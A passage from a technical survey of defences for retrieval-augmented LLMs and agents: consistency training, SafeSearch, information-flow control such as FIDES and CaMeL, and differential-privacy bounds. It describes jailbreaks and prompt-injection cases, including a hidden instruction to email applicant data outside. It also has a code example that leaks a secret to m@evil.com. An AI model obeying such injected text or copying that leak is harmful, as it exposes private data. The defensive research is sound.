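L(θ) = −log Pθ(y | wrapped prompt),

where θ stands for the model's weights and Pθ for the probability the model assigns. The loss falls as the model becomes more likely to repeat its original refusal despite the jailbreak.

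Activation consistency training (ACT) compares internal activity instead:

L(θ) = average of ‖hθ(wrapped prompt) − h₀(clean prompt)‖².

Here hθ is the model's activations during training and h₀ its activations before training. The average covers every layer, but only the tokens that both prompts end with.

For the jailbreak data, Irpan and colleagues kept only pairs in which the model refused the clean prompt and answered the wrapped one. This left 830 to 1,330 pairs, depending on the model. They then tested on other requests, with some jailbreaks from training and some new ones. These are the shares of prompts that Gemini 2.5 Flash answered:

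| Training | Harmful (ClearHarm) | Harmful (WildguardTest) | Harmless (XSTest) | Harmless (WildJailbreak) |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | 67.8% | 47.2% | 89.5% | 98.1% |
| BCT | 2.9% | 8.4% | 77.9% | 73.1% |
| ACT | 52.2% | 24.0% | 81.4% | 95.2% |

BCT worked much better against jailbreaks, but the model then refused about a quarter of the WildJailbreak prompts, which are harmless but look dangerous. The two harmless sets have just 86 and 105 prompts, so differences of a few points mean little, but a 25-point fall in the answer rate is well outside the margin of error. Gemma 3 27B's answer rate on these prompts fell less, from 97.1% to 89.4%.

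The needless refusals probably occurred because every target response in the training data was a refusal, so nothing rewarded the model for answering. Irpan and colleagues expect that mixing in harmless requests would help. Xue, Qi and colleagues (2026) explain in *Deactivating Refusal Triggers* that models trained to refuse harmful requests also learn to refuse in response to harmless wording in those requests. Similarly, if every training example with documents ended in a refusal, the model might learn to refuse whenever it is given documents.

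### Matching the decision and not the answer

BCT would be easy to apply to the police-chase request. The wrapped prompt would contain the five Wikipedia passages, and the target would be Llama-3-8B's own refusal. BCT is harder to apply to harmless questions, because a retrieved document is supposed to change the answer, while a jailbreak should have no effect on it. The target would be the answer the model gives without documents, so the model would learn to ignore them. ACT has the same problem, because it pulls the activations towards their values without documents.

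Context invariance only requires the decision to refuse to stay the same. A method from Imran, Gupta and colleagues (2026), in *Consistency Training while Mitigating Obfuscation via Rate Matching*, fits this better. It samples many responses to both versions of a prompt and compares how often one chosen behaviour occurs. If that behaviour were refusal, each response to the version with documents would earn the reward

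r = −(p − p₀)(T − p),

where p is the refusal rate with documents, p₀ is the rate without them, and T is 1 for a refusal and 0 for anything else. Suppose the model refuses a harmful request 90% of the time alone and 60% of the time with documents. A refusal then earns 0.3 × 0.4 = 0.12, and an answer earns 0.3 × (−0.6) = −0.18, so training raises the refusal rate. For a harmless question that the model refuses more often with documents, the signs reverse. The content of the answer doesn't affect the reward, so the model can still use the documents.

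A developer could also apply the reward only when p is below p₀. Documents could then make the model refuse more often but not less often, which is what the office assistant with the restraining order needs.

Imran and colleagues tested this on sycophancy, not refusal. They trained two models with one kind of misleading cue in multiple-choice questions and tested them with five other kinds. BCT reduced the effect of the trained cue more than rate matching did. Both methods worked equally well on the other five cues for Llama-3.1-8B, but only rate matching helped GPT-oss-20B on average. BCT also made both models less likely to mention a cue that had changed their answer. In a retrieval system, this would make it harder for someone reading the model's reasoning to notice that a document had influenced a refusal. Rate matching mostly avoided this side effect, but it needed 256 sampled responses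 for each training question.

Neither method can make a model safer with documents than it already is without them. Irpan and colleagues point out that consistency training can make a model consistently unsafe, so they discarded requests that the model answered when given the request alone.

### Whether the training carries over to new text

BCT trains on responses recorded in advance. Han, Fujimoto and colleagues (2026), in *On-Policy Consistency Training Improves LLM Safety with Minimal Capability Degradation*, instead had the model write a new response to the wrapped prompt at every step. A frozen copy of the original model then scored each token as if it had seen only the clean prompt, and training reduced

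log Pθ(token | wrapped prompt) − log P₀(token | clean prompt).

They tested both methods by training a separate attacker model against each target. On requests held out from training, attacks on the BCT-trained models succeeded about 12% of the time for Qwen3-4B and 4% for Qwen3-8B. With the new method, the rates were about 0% and 1%. The paper's abstract gives a higher average failure rate for BCT than these figures suggest. BCT also reduced GPT-oss-20B to single-digit accuracy on three general tests, while the new method preserved much more of the model's ability. Much of the damage from BCT therefore seems to come from how it trains the model rather than from the goal of consistency. But the new method still compares whole responses, so it would also teach a model to ignore documents if a developer used it on harmless questions.

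In *Consistency Training Along the Transformer Stack*, Gautam, Shah and colleagues (2026) ran the closest test to one with harmless documents. A series of biographical facts about someone like Hitler, each harmless by itself, can lead a model to speak as that person and adopt his views. They trained Gemma-3-27B on 200 examples in which facts about Hitler came before a question, with the model's answer to the question alone as the target. They then tested it with up to 32 facts about each of 44 real or fictional people, 43 of whom were not in the training data. After BCT, the model no longer adopted any of these identities.

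This is encouraging because the model learned to resist harmless text on subjects it hadn't trained on. However, the test used facts chosen to add up to a persona, and it didn't measure whether the model refused harmful requests. Gautam and colleagues also found that one version of the training, which used activations to keep the model calm after repeated criticism, made it worse at refusing harmful requests. A developer should therefore retest refusal without documents after any such training.

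### Rewarding an agent for safe searches

Zhan, Budiman-Chan and colleagues (2025), in *SafeSearch*, did train with retrieved documents in the input, though not for consistency. They used reinforcement learning on agents that write their own queries and search Wikipedia up to three times. The training mixed 79,168 ordinary questions, which earned a reward for a correct answer, with 12,204 harmful requests. For a harmful request, an LLM judge scored the final response:

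- An unsafe response earned −1.5.
- A safe response earned 1 to 4 points for helpfulness. A flat refusal earned 1, and a response with useful and safe alternatives could earn 3.

The judge also labelled each search query, adding a small reward for a safe one and a penalty 3.5 times as large for an unsafe one.

These are the harmful-response rates for Qwen2.5-7B on three sets of harmful requests. The third set, WildTeaming, consists of jailbreaks.

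| Version | Red-teaming benchmark | StrongREJECT | WildTeaming |
|---|---|---|---|
| No search | 16.2% | 14.3% | 81.7% |
| Search agent before training | 29.1% | 27.3% | 83.9% |
| Trained only to answer correctly | 32.4% | 36.3% | 87.3% |
| SafeSearch | 2.2% | 0.2% | 1.9% |
| SafeSearch, scored by another judge | 7.2% | 5.9% | 15.7% |

The SafeSearch agent stayed as useful as the one trained only to answer correctly. Both got 54.9% of questions right on one trivia test, and SafeSearch did slightly better on two harder tests. The smaller Qwen2.5-3B improved less and still gave harmful responses to 48.9% of the jailbreaks.

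The last row of the table is the fairer estimate of safety. GPT-oss-20B judged the other rows and also set the training rewards, so the agent may have learned to satisfy that judge in particular. When Claude Sonnet 4 judged both trained agents, SafeSearch reduced harm by 79–85%, compared with 93–99% under GPT-oss-20B.

SafeSearch refused 12.1% of 300 harmless prompts that look dangerous, compared with 5.4% for the agent before training. When trained without the points for helpfulness, the agent refused 27.3%. Rewarding useful alternatives to a flat refusal is therefore probably worth copying.

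Zhan and colleagues also tested filters on the agent trained only to answer correctly. Blocking unsafe queries lowered its rate on the first set from 32.4% to 30.5%, and removing unsafe documents lowered it to 31.7%. The second result agrees with the estimate from An and colleagues' data that cleaning the collection would prevent only a small share of unsafe responses.

### Not searching is different from refusing

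SafeSearch also made the agent search much less. The share of responses that involved a search fell from 72.8% to 21.8% on the first set of harmful requests and from 68.6% to 4.9% on StrongREJECT. An agent that doesn't search never sees a document, so these results don't show how it would respond with one in its input. Zhan and colleagues could test this by pasting on-topic passages into the prompt.

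A model can answer a harmful request without retrieving anything, or retrieve a page while refusing the request. Nawal, Baser and Gurusamy (2026), in *Before Retrieval Begins*, gave seven open models harmful requests with a web address and a tool for fetching the page. Mistral-7B fetched the page for only 7.8% of the requests but gave harmful responses to 67.2%, mostly from its training rather than a fetched page. Across all seven models, 33.6% of the fetches for harmful requests came with a written refusal in the same turn.

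They then fine-tuned each model on 80 harmful requests with written refusals and 80 ordinary instructions, none of which involved tools. Afterwards, three models fetched pages for harmful requests less often, by 20, 55 and 62 percentage points, and still fetched at least 94.9% of pages for harmless summaries. The other four lost some or all of their ability to use the tool properly. Each result comes from a single training run, so the differences between models may be partly due to chance.

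Ordinary refusal training can therefore carry over to tools, but a developer can't count on it. *MLLMs Fail to Refuse when Using Tools Agentically* (2026) tested models that read images as well as text, and every model's rate of failing to refuse was higher when it had tools. Claude Opus 4.6 had the lowest rate without tools, and its rate still rose from 13.6% to 18.1% with them.

### Changing refusal at run time

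An operator who can't train the model can try safety prompts or fetch the page before the harmful request arrives, though neither helped every model. Other methods change the model's activations or its input.

SafeRAG-Steering, the method Maskey and colleagues used to reduce needless refusals, adds a fixed vector to the activations at one layer. They tuned it to get as many direct answers as possible, with no penalty for answering harmful requests. Their test set included 232 harmful requests, but they report no steering results for those requests.

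Steering of this kind doesn't directly produce context invariance either. Since v is the same for every input, adding it shifts the activations with and without documents equally towards answering, leaving the difference between them unchanged at that layer. An operator could subtract v to get more refusals, but this would probably bring back needless ones.

Retrieval can also strengthen refusal. *Training-Free Refusal of MCP Exploits via Retrieval-Augmented Generation* (Halloran, 2026) studied harmful commands to agents with the suspicious wording removed, such as a request to add an attacker's login key to a settings file. Its method, RAG-Pref, retrieves examples of good and bad responses to similar commands and tells the model to follow the good ones and avoid the bad ones. RAG-Pref roughly tripled refusals of these commands on average across five open models. Fine-tuning on preferred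 and rejected responses did not raise any model's refusal rate above 47%, though combining it with RAG-Pref worked better than either alone. These figures cover only attacks, so they don't show how many harmless commands the models would refuse.

Halloran's proof that the bad examples reduce uncertainty about the response, beyond what the good ones do, doesn't explain the rise in refusals, because the theorem would also hold for a model that became more certain to obey. He also suggests that ordinary RAG weakens refusal by retrieving examples of attacks without examples of refusing them. That can't be the whole explanation, because An and colleagues found large rises in unsafe responses when none of the passages contained a harmful answer.

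A third method separates the decision to refuse from the rest of the task. Agents usually receive descriptions of their tools in a structured format. *Tool Specifications Matter* (Pan, Yang and colleagues, 2026) found that Llama-3.1-8B refused 58% of harmful requests in ordinary chat but only 3% as an agent, and attributed most of the weakening of refusal measured inside the model to the structured format. The paper's safeguard, SafeKeep, first asks the model to judge the request with the tools described in plain text, and uses the structured descriptions only if the request passes. SafeKeep raised the average refusal rate across four models from 23.8% to 70.6%. If an operator ran such a check before retrieving any documents, its result couldn't depend on them.

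### Why a lower rate is still claim (a)

After BCT, Gemini 2.5 Flash still answered about 31 of the 1,068 harmful ClearHarm prompts, and any one of those answers disproves claim (b), that the model refuses whatever the input. Even a perfect score wouldn't have established (b), because training lowers the average loss on examples a developer chose and doesn't limit the loss on any other input.

The results don't establish (c) either, because none of these studies compares the trained model's decisions on the same requests with and without documents. A model can give fewer harmful responses with documents because it refuses more requests of every kind.

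How far a lower rate is likely to carry over depends on what was new in the test:

| Method | Added text in training | New in the test | Still untested |
|---|---|---|---|
| BCT and ACT (Irpan et al.) | Jailbreaks | Requests and some jailbreaks | Retrieved documents |
| Rate matching (Imran et al.) | One kind of misleading cue | Five other kinds | Refusal, retrieved documents |
| BCT on personas (Gautam et al.) | Facts about Hitler | Facts about 43 others | Harmful requests with retrieved documents |
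| SafeSearch (Zhan et al.) | Wikipedia passages | Two sets of harmful requests | Other collections, the open web |
| SafeRAG-Steering (Maskey et al.) | Three to seven documents | Questions in the same six fields | New fields, longer sets, agents |

Longer inputs may expose other weaknesses. *Do Reasoning LLMs Refuse What They Infer in Long Contexts?* (2026) reports tests of two safety-trained versions of a 7-billion-parameter model. Both gave only safe responses when a long text stated the harmful request directly. When they had to infer the request from fragments, 18% of one version's responses and 45% of the other's were unsafe.

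Indira Saravanan and Fraser's four document conditions would work well for testing consistency training directly. A developer could train a model on half of their 20 categories of harm, using Wikipedia articles as the documents, then test it on the other half with web pages, longer documents and an agent that searches repeatedly. The test should also include harmless questions that the model can answer only from the documents, to check that it hasn't learned to ignore documents.

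## Enforcing guarantees by tracking where text came from

Training and filtering both rely on a model to make the right decision. Information-flow control uses ordinary code to limit what a model's mistakes can affect, based on where each piece of text came from. Researchers have mostly used it to stop prompt injection in agents, but the same code can limit the influence of any document, including a benign one.

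### Labels, policies and exceptions

In *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025) attach two kinds of label to data. An integrity label marks data as trusted, like the user's request, or untrusted, like a web page that a stranger could have edited. A confidentiality label lists who may read the data.

Combined data carries the restrictions of all its sources' labels. A summary that depends on a trusted request and an untrusted page is untrusted. If Ana, Ben and Cai may read one file, and Ben, Cai and Dee may read another, only Ben and Cai may read a summary of both. A model's output is normally labeled as if it depended on the whole input, because nobody can reliably tell which parts the model used.

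Before each tool call, a short program compares the labels with a policy. One policy allows an action with real consequences only if no untrusted text influenced the choice to take it. Another allows data to go only to people permitted to read it. A policy can also treat the parts of a call differently. For example, it can require an email's recipient to come from a trusted source but allow untrusted text in the body.

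Because labels only get stricter, more and more of a system's data ends up labeled untrusted or secret, which is called label creep. In *The Limits of Information-Flow Control Enforcement for Agentic Systems*, Gregory, Domico and colleagues (2026) simulated thousands of tasks without running a language model. Connecting agents more directly and giving the sensitive tools to only a few of them slowed label creep, but no arrangement they tested prevented it.

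Practical systems therefore need deliberate exceptions. Endorsement relabels untrusted data as trusted, and declassification lets more people read secret data. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (Kolluri, Sharma et al., 2026) gives the example of a harmless email that lists ten jobs for an agent. If the user endorses the email, the agent can do all ten. Otherwise, the user has to approve each one separately.

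### Why the model can be untrustworthy

Suppose a policy requires an email's recipient to be trusted. If the labels are correct, no component that helped choose the recipient received the retrieved page, so a different page would have led to the same recipient. This property is called noninterference. It holds even if the model behaves badly, because it depends only on what text the model received.

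The labels have to account for a program's decisions as well as the data it copies. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *The LLMbda Calculus*, show how this can go wrong with a program along these lines, where the bank balance is secret:

```
rich = True
tmp = True
if balance > threshold: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

The program sends the email only if the balance is above the threshold. When it is, the line that sets `rich` to False never runs, so a system that updates labels only on lines that run will leave `rich` labelled public. CaMeL, a well-known defence for agents, had this flaw.

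Garby and colleagues designed a small programming language for agents, LLMbda, that tracks such decisions. They proved a form of noninterference for every program in it, apart from deliberate exceptions, and checked the proof by computer. The theorem assumes nothing about how the model behaves. It also covers probabilities, which McLean had left for future work. Suppose two runs start with inputs that differ only in data an observer may not see, and let μ and ν be the probabilities of what the observer sees in each. The statistical distance between them is then at most

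½ × (chance that the first run doesn't finish + chance that the second doesn't finish).

If both runs always finish, every outcome the observer can see is equally likely in both. If each run fails to finish 2% of the time, the probability of any such outcome can differ between them by at most two percentage points.

### CaMeL plans before it reads

Edoardo Debenedetti and colleagues introduced CaMeL in 2025. It follows the programmer Simon Willison's idea of splitting an agent between two models, so that the one with power over tools never reads untrusted text. Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues (2026), in *CaMeLoT*, describe how it works:

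1. A privileged model reads the user's request and writes a Python program for the whole task, before any tool has returned anything.
2. An interpreter runs the program and calls the tools.
3. When the program needs information from a piece of text, it calls a quarantined model, which reads the text but has no tools of its own.
4. The interpreter records where every value came from and who may read it. Before each tool call, it runs a policy that allows or denies the call. One policy lets the agent change a password only if the new password came from a trusted source.

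This gives CaMeL control-flow integrity, which means the agent can only follow paths already in the program. A retrieved page can still determine which of those paths the agent takes, so this guarantee is weaker than noninterference. Garby and colleagues note that CaMeL has no theorem comparable to theirs, and that its developers called formalizing it a "crucial direction" for further work.

### FIDES hides what it retrieves

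FIDES, which Costa and colleagues built at Microsoft, chooses its actions one at a time. When a tool returns data with a stricter label than the conversation so far, FIDES stores the data in a variable and shows the planning model only the variable's name. The planning model can pass the variable to another tool or have a quarantined model answer a question about the data.

The planning model can also open the variable, but the conversation then becomes untrusted and the policy blocks most consequential actions. As a compromise, the quarantined model can be restricted to answering yes or no. A policy may allow such an answer because it lets a page influence the agent by only one bit.

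Costa and colleagues prove that FIDES can enforce explicit secrecy, a weaker property than noninterference. Explicit secrecy prevents the agent from copying a secret to a place where others can see it, but an observer might still learn something about the secret from which actions the agent takes. The researchers decided against noninterference because it would essentially forbid any publicly visible action after the agent had read a secret.

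### Emailing a summary of retrieved pages

Suppose a user asks an agent to find web pages on battery recycling and email a summary to dana@example.com. An agent like FIDES could handle this in three calls:

| Call | Labels | Result |
|---|---|---|
| Search for "battery recycling" | Search terms trusted | Allowed, and the pages go into the variable PAGES, labelled untrusted |
| Have the quarantined model summarize PAGES | Instruction trusted, pages untrusted | Allowed, and the text goes into SUMMARY, labelled untrusted |
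| Email SUMMARY to dana@example.com | Choice of action and recipient trusted, body untrusted | Allowed |

The planning model never receives the pages, so nothing in them can change the recipient, but the pages can still make the summary wrong. Costa and colleagues note that an instruction hidden in the text could make the quarantined model return an empty summary.

Now suppose the user asks the agent to send the summary to the contact address on the first page. The quarantined model extracts the address, which inherits the page's untrusted label. The policy blocks the email even if the address is genuine, because whoever wrote the page would be choosing the recipient. The agent could send the email if the user looked at the address and endorsed it.

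### What the protection costs

AgentDojo tests agents on 97 tasks, with and without attacks hidden in the data they read. Costa and colleagues used it to compare FIDES with an ordinary agent, using GPT-4o for both. These are the shares of tasks completed when there was no attack:

| Tasks | Ordinary agent | Ordinary agent with policies | FIDES without policies | FIDES with policies |
|---|---|---|---|---|
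| Office work | 75.0% | 37.0% | 63.5% | 59.0% |
| Travel | 70.0% | 73.0% | 50.0% | 41.0% |
| Banking | 98.8% | 37.5% | 65.0% | 52.5% |
| Slack | 93.3% | 20.0% | 63.8% | 47.6% |

Without policies, 152 attacks succeeded against the ordinary agent and 21 against FIDES. With policies, none succeeded against either agent after Costa and colleagues excluded cases they thought AgentDojo had misjudged. Hiding text in variables helps an agent finish tasks that the policies would otherwise block. Even so, FIDES completed only about half of the tasks. Some of the failures were intended, since many banking tasks ask the agent to read a file and do what it says.

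Other researchers have rerun CaMeL on AgentDojo. *SecureClaw* (2026), which presents a rival system, reports that none of 629 attacks succeeded against CaMeL, but CaMeL completed only 29 of the 97 harmless tasks. Nikolaou and colleagues ran it with Claude Haiku 4.5, and it completed 49. Garby and colleagues tested it only on the banking tasks, where it completed 37.5% with its policies and about 70% without them.

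Newer systems recover some of this loss. Kolluri and colleagues tell the planning model about the labels and policies so it can avoid plans the policies would block. With the model o3-mini, their agent completed 59.1% of tasks without human approval, compared with 50.1% for FIDES. Garby and colleagues' agent chooses its endorsements before it reads any untrusted data. It completed 75% of the banking tasks with GPT-5.2, and attacks succeeded in only two of 1,296 attacked runs across three models.

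Much of the remaining loss in task completion depends on whether a person is available to approve exceptions. *Flowsh* (2026) adds labels to the command line that an agent uses. The agent completed 88.2% of one set of tasks with approvals, but 58.8% when every violation was blocked. Token use also varies between systems. In *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (2026), a CaMeL-based agent used 1.88 times as many tokens as an unprotected one. A FIDES-based agent used 29.6 times as many as the unprotected one, because it sent the full history back to the planning model at every step.

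### CaMeL agents that call each other

CaMeL's guarantee can fail when several CaMeL agents work together. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, 2026) connected three agents, one to coordinate the others, one to read a database and one to send messages. The user asked them to send Julie a Slack message summarizing the job applicants, but the database contained a hidden instruction to email the data to an outside address.

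The first two agents followed the same programs as they would have without the attack. But the coordinator put the summary, with the hidden instruction still in it, into its request to the messaging agent. The messaging agent treated that request as coming from a trusted user, so it wrote a program that also sent the email.

Each agent's guarantee assumes that its instructions are trusted, and the coordinator broke that assumption for the messaging agent. Peters-Gill and colleagues fixed the problem by sending instructions and data separately and keeping the labels attached to the data. Averaged over five models, attacks on their multi-agent version of AgentDojo succeeded 12.9% of the time without CaMeL, 0.2% of the time with separate CaMeL agents, and never with the fix.

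GPT-5.5 resisted every attack in this test without CaMeL. Peters-Gill and colleagues warn that stronger attacks might still work, since attackers in a large public competition succeeded against every leading model tested. Labels are still worth using with such a model because their protection doesn't depend on which attacks a tester tried.

### Why labels don't stop the police-chase guide

None of this would have stopped the guide to escaping the police. FIDES would label the user's request trusted and the Wikipedia passages untrusted. A quarantined model could then read the passages and write the guide, and the agent would show it to the user without sending anything to anyone else or changing any files. Costa and colleagues treat answering the user as inconsequential, so the policies would allow it.

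Different labels wouldn't help, because a label records where text came from, not whether it is harmful. These systems also trust the user by design, and in the police-chase case the harmful part is the user's own request. Kolluri and colleagues explicitly exclude jailbreaks from the attacks they try to prevent.

The two successful attacks on Garby and colleagues' agent show a similar limit. The user had asked the agent to read a file and make the payment it described, but an attacker had replaced the file. Following the file was what the user wanted, so the agent could have avoided the payment only by judging the contents suspicious or by refusing to act on any file.

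Splitting the work between two models might even make refusal less reliable. The quarantined model may receive only a narrow instruction, such as to list the driving techniques in a set of passages, without the user's stated purpose.

### Deciding whether to refuse before reading

Still, *From Agent Traces to Trust* (2026), a survey of these methods, concludes that "unsafe behavior can arise from influence, not content alone". This fits An and colleagues' experiment, in which harmless passages influenced the model's decision to refuse. Labels can control this influence if the system treats refusal as an action that only trusted text may affect.

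CaMeL writes its plan before it reads anything, and a RAG system could decide whether to refuse in the same way. The following design is a derivation from that idea and not a feature of CaMeL or FIDES:

1. Send the model the request alone, with the same instruction that the tester used in the refusal test. This is the input (i′, q).
2. If the response is a refusal, show it to the user and don't search.
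3. Otherwise, discard the response, retrieve the documents D, and have the model answer from (i, D, q).
4. Allow further refusals after the search, but never let a document reverse a refusal from the first step.

Let a(q) be the probability that the first step does not refuse request q. The system can't give a harmful answer without passing this step, so for every request q and every set of documents D,

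P(harmful answer to q, given D) ≤ a(q).

The proof needs no assumption about how documents affect the model, so the bound holds for both poisoned and benign documents. It also holds for an agent that searches many times, because nothing the agent finds can return to the first step.

With this design, a refusal test run without documents also applies to the whole system, because the system makes its first decision from the same input the test used, (i′, q). If the first step refuses 970 of 1,000 harmful requests, at most 30 of them can get a harmful answer, whatever the retriever returns. For new requests, the test result is as good evidence about the system as it would be about the model alone.

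The tester has to count refusals, not just harmless responses. When Llama-3-8B was given no documents, some of its safe responses may have been harmless advice instead of refusals. The requests that received such advice would pass the first step, so a(q) could average more than the model's 0.3% rate of unsafe responses.

Asking for a one-word verdict in the first step would save time, but that version would need its own test, because Epifantsev and colleagues found that requiring a single-letter answer can suppress refusal. An input filter applied only to the request would give the same kind of bound, with its miss rate in place of a(q).

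Because of step 4, the system satisfies only a one-way form of context invariance. The office assistant could therefore still refuse after finding the restraining order, but this design does not ensure that it would.

### What an early decision misses

The biggest gap is in handling harmless-looking requests about dangerous pages, such as Nawal and colleagues' neutral summary requests, which Llama Guard 3 flagged only when it was also given the page. Nothing in these requests would make the first step refuse them. The bound still holds, but a(q) is close to 1, so it rules out almost nothing. An operator worried about such requests needs a check on the documents or the finished answer.

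Follow-up messages are also difficult, because label creep occurs within a conversation. If a user writes "explain step three in more detail", the meaning depends on the previous answer, which may depend on retrieved documents. The answer is therefore untrusted, and the first step can't read it without losing the guarantee. The first step can safely read everything the user has typed, but this won't always reveal what "step three" was.

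The design also can't use documents to correct a needless refusal. An operator of a legal research tool could reduce such refusals by adding a fixed description of the collection to the first instruction, such as that the assistant searches published statutes. The operator writes this description before any search, so the retrieved text can't influence it. But adding it changes i′, so the operator would have to repeat the refusal test with the new instruction.

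A FIDES policy might let documents reverse a refusal through a yes-or-no answer. This is risky because, although one bit has little influence on an email or a calendar entry, it is enough to turn a refusal into an answer.

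## Guarantees that allow a small error and say how it adds up

Having the model decide whether to refuse before it reads the retrieved documents gives a bound that holds for every document, but only because documents can't affect that decision, though they should affect the rest of the answer. Researchers in privacy, copyright and statistics have developed guarantees that allow a limited effect or a limited error rate, and some include a rule for adding up errors across many answers.

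### Differential privacy

*Composition of Differential Privacy & Privacy Amplification by Subsampling* (2022) describes an employer who sees a regularly updated count of people with a condition such as cancer. The count isn't specific to anyone, but if it rises on the day you start work, the employer can combine two facts that are harmless on their own and guess that you have the condition.

Differential privacy limits what such combinations can reveal. Two datasets D and D′ are neighbours if they differ in one person's data, or in one document. A randomized procedure M is (ε, δ)-differentially private if, for all neighbours D and D′ and every set S of outputs,

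P(M(D) is in S) ≤ e^ε × P(M(D′) is in S) + δ.

If δ is 0 and ε is 0.1, including your data makes any output at most about 10.5% more likely. A positive δ allows small exceptions. M can meet the definition for a count by adding random noise before releasing the number.

This limit holds whatever else an observer knows. By Bayes' rule, seeing an output multiplies the observer's odds that your data is present by P(output | D) / P(output | D′). When δ is 0, this ratio always lies between e^−ε and e^ε, whatever knowledge the original odds were based on. *The Promise of Differential Privacy* (Dwork, 2011) describes a promise that holds regardless of other studies and datasets. The definition itself allows for outside knowledge, as auxiliary input does in zero-knowledge proofs.

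The limits also add up when someone asks k questions, even if each question depends on the earlier answers. When δ = 0, each answer contributes a factor of at most e^ε, so k answers contribute at most e^(kε). When δ > 0, basic composition gives a total of (kε, kδ).

Advanced composition gives a smaller total when ε is small. Each answer may point towards your data being present or away from it, so the answers partly cancel out. As *Advances in Differential Privacy and Differentially Private Machine Learning* (2024) states the theorem, the total is (ε′, kδ + δ′), where

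ε′ = ε√(2k ln(1/δ′)) + kε(e^ε − 1).

Take ε = 0.1, k = 100 and δ′ = 0.00001:

- Basic composition gives 100 × 0.1 = 10.
- Advanced composition gives 4.80 + 1.05 = 5.85.

The first total allows an output to be about 22,000 times more likely with your data than without it. The second lowers this to about 350 times in exchange for the extra δ′. *Advanced Composition* (Smith, 2025) points out that no total smaller than kε holds in general while δ stays at zero, so some such exchange is necessary.

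### Private documents in a retrieval system

Zhang (2026), in *From One Query to Many*, reviews five RAG systems that use differential privacy to protect their documents. One common design splits the retrieved documents into groups, runs the model on each group, and releases only a noisy combination of the results. The systems differ in how they handle many questions:

- Three protect each answer separately. Their developers often test them at an ε of 5 or 10 per answer. At 10, basic composition gives a total of 1,000 after 100 answers, and advanced composition can't improve on this because it only helps when ε is below about 0.69.
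- One gives each document a budget and stops using the document once the budget runs out. The total for any one document stays fixed, but popular documents disappear. If each document may be used once, a document relevant to a quarter of all questions has a half-life of fewer than three questions.
- One writes a synthetic collection in advance and answers only from that. Its total never grows, but anything the synthetic text left out is unavailable to every later question.

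Zhang found no argument based on real use for setting ε to 10, and concludes that the value reflects where the methods start to become useful. In two sets of tests at that value, attempts to detect whether a document was in the collection did about as well as guessing. The guarantee doesn't explain this result, since an ε of 10 would permit almost perfect detection. Displaying the retrieved documents as sources breaks the guarantee at any ε.

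These systems protect the documents' contents but don't limit what users do. Llama-3-8B's police-chase guide wouldn't violate differential privacy, because Wikipedia passages aren't private.

The same inequality could protect refusal in principle. Suppose that adding or removing one passage never changed the probability of any response by more than a factor of e^ε. Removing five passages one at a time would then give

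P(harmful response with five passages) ≤ e^(5ε) × P(harmful response with none).

This would be a version of context invariance (c) with a stated error. To keep Llama-3-8B's 0.3% below 1%, ε would have to be at most 0.24. But a system with such a small ε could hardly use its passages. The most efficient of the per-answer systems in Zhang's review starts to outperform a model without retrieval at an ε of about 2, where the factor for five passages is about 22,000. (Those systems also define ε for changes to the collection, where removing a passage lets the next one take its place.)

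A more practical guarantee would limit only the documents' effect on refusal and let them change the answer's content freely. Making the refusal decision before retrieval is the extreme case, where ε is zero for that first decision.

### Counting what a user learns

Claim (d), limited learning, needs a limit on how much a user learns about something dangerous. Glukhov, Han and colleagues (2024), in *Breach By A Thousand Leaks*, propose one. They start with a harmful question that has a set A of forbidden answers. Before using the model, the user believes answer a with probability p(a), and after reading the responses h, with probability p(a | h). The leakage is the average, over the responses the model might give, of

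Σ p(a | h) × ln(p(a | h) / p(a)), summed over the answers a in A.

If a user's confidence in a forbidden answer goes from 25% to 90%, the result is 0.9 × ln(0.9/0.25), or about 1.15. The factor of 0.9 gives more weight to answers the user ends up believing. Without it, a rise from 0.1% to 0.9% would count as much as a rise from 10% to 90%.

A safeguard has limit ε if no single question leaks more than ε to any user in a chosen set. This makes the assumption about users explicit, though someone still has to choose the set. For k questions fixed in advance, Glukhov and colleagues' theorem puts the total leakage at no more than

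kε + a term for dependence between the answers.

The second term is needed for cases like the secret split into shares, where each answer alone leaks nothing, so kε is zero. In a retrieval system, answers based on the same document could easily be related in this way.

The theorem isn't quite right as stated, because its dependence term covers only the cases in which a forbidden answer is correct. Suppose a user thinks there is a 50% chance that a forbidden answer is correct, and asks two questions whose replies each look like a fair coin flip. The replies are independent if the forbidden answer is correct and always match if it isn't. Neither reply is informative alone and the dependence term is zero, so the theorem's bound on leakage is zero. But two replies that differ prove the forbidden answer correct, and the average leakage is about 0.07.

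The proof mistakenly treats a sum over the forbidden answers as if it covered all answers. One can repair the rule by defining both ε and the dependence term with mutual information, a standard measure that counts changes in the user's belief in every answer. Glukhov and colleagues reasonably avoided this measure because it would also count a user becoming confident of a harmless answer as a failure.

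Meeting the limit can make a model nearly useless. Glukhov and colleagues give an example of a safeguard that returns the model's response with probability t and an empty reply otherwise, where t is ε divided by the leakage of the worst possible question. Suppose the leakage of that question is 1.15, the answers are independent, and the operator wants a total leakage of at most 0.1 over 100 answers. Then ε is 0.001, and the safeguard returns fewer than one response in 1,000. An operator could apply it only to risky questions, but would first have to recognize them. Glukhov and colleagues also derive a limit on what an honest user can learn under any such safeguard. This limit is tightest when the honest question is close to the forbidden one.

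Glukhov and colleagues' composition rule covers only questions fixed in advance. This restriction is also serious, because real users and agents that search repeatedly choose their next question after reading the last answer. Differential privacy's composition rules do cover this case.

### Voting across passages

*Certifiably Robust RAG against Retrieval Corruption* (Xiang, Wu and colleagues, 2024) presents RobustRAG, a defense against attackers who plant passages in the search results. RobustRAG limits how many passages can affect an answer. The model answers from each passage separately, and the system then combines the answers.

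The simplest version is a vote on a multiple-choice question. Suppose the system retrieves ten passages and an attacker can plant k′ of them, pushing out the lowest-ranked ones. The other 10 − k′ passages are untouched, and so are their votes. If the winner leads by more than k′ among these, the planted passages can't change the result:

| Planted passages | Votes from the others | Lead | Is the result certain? |
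|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | 6 for A, 3 for B | 3 | Yes |
| 1 | 5 for A, 4 for B | 1 | No, the planted passage could force a tie |
| 2 | 6 for A, 2 for B | 4 | Yes |
| 5 | 4 for A, 1 for B | 3 | No, B could win 6 to 4 |

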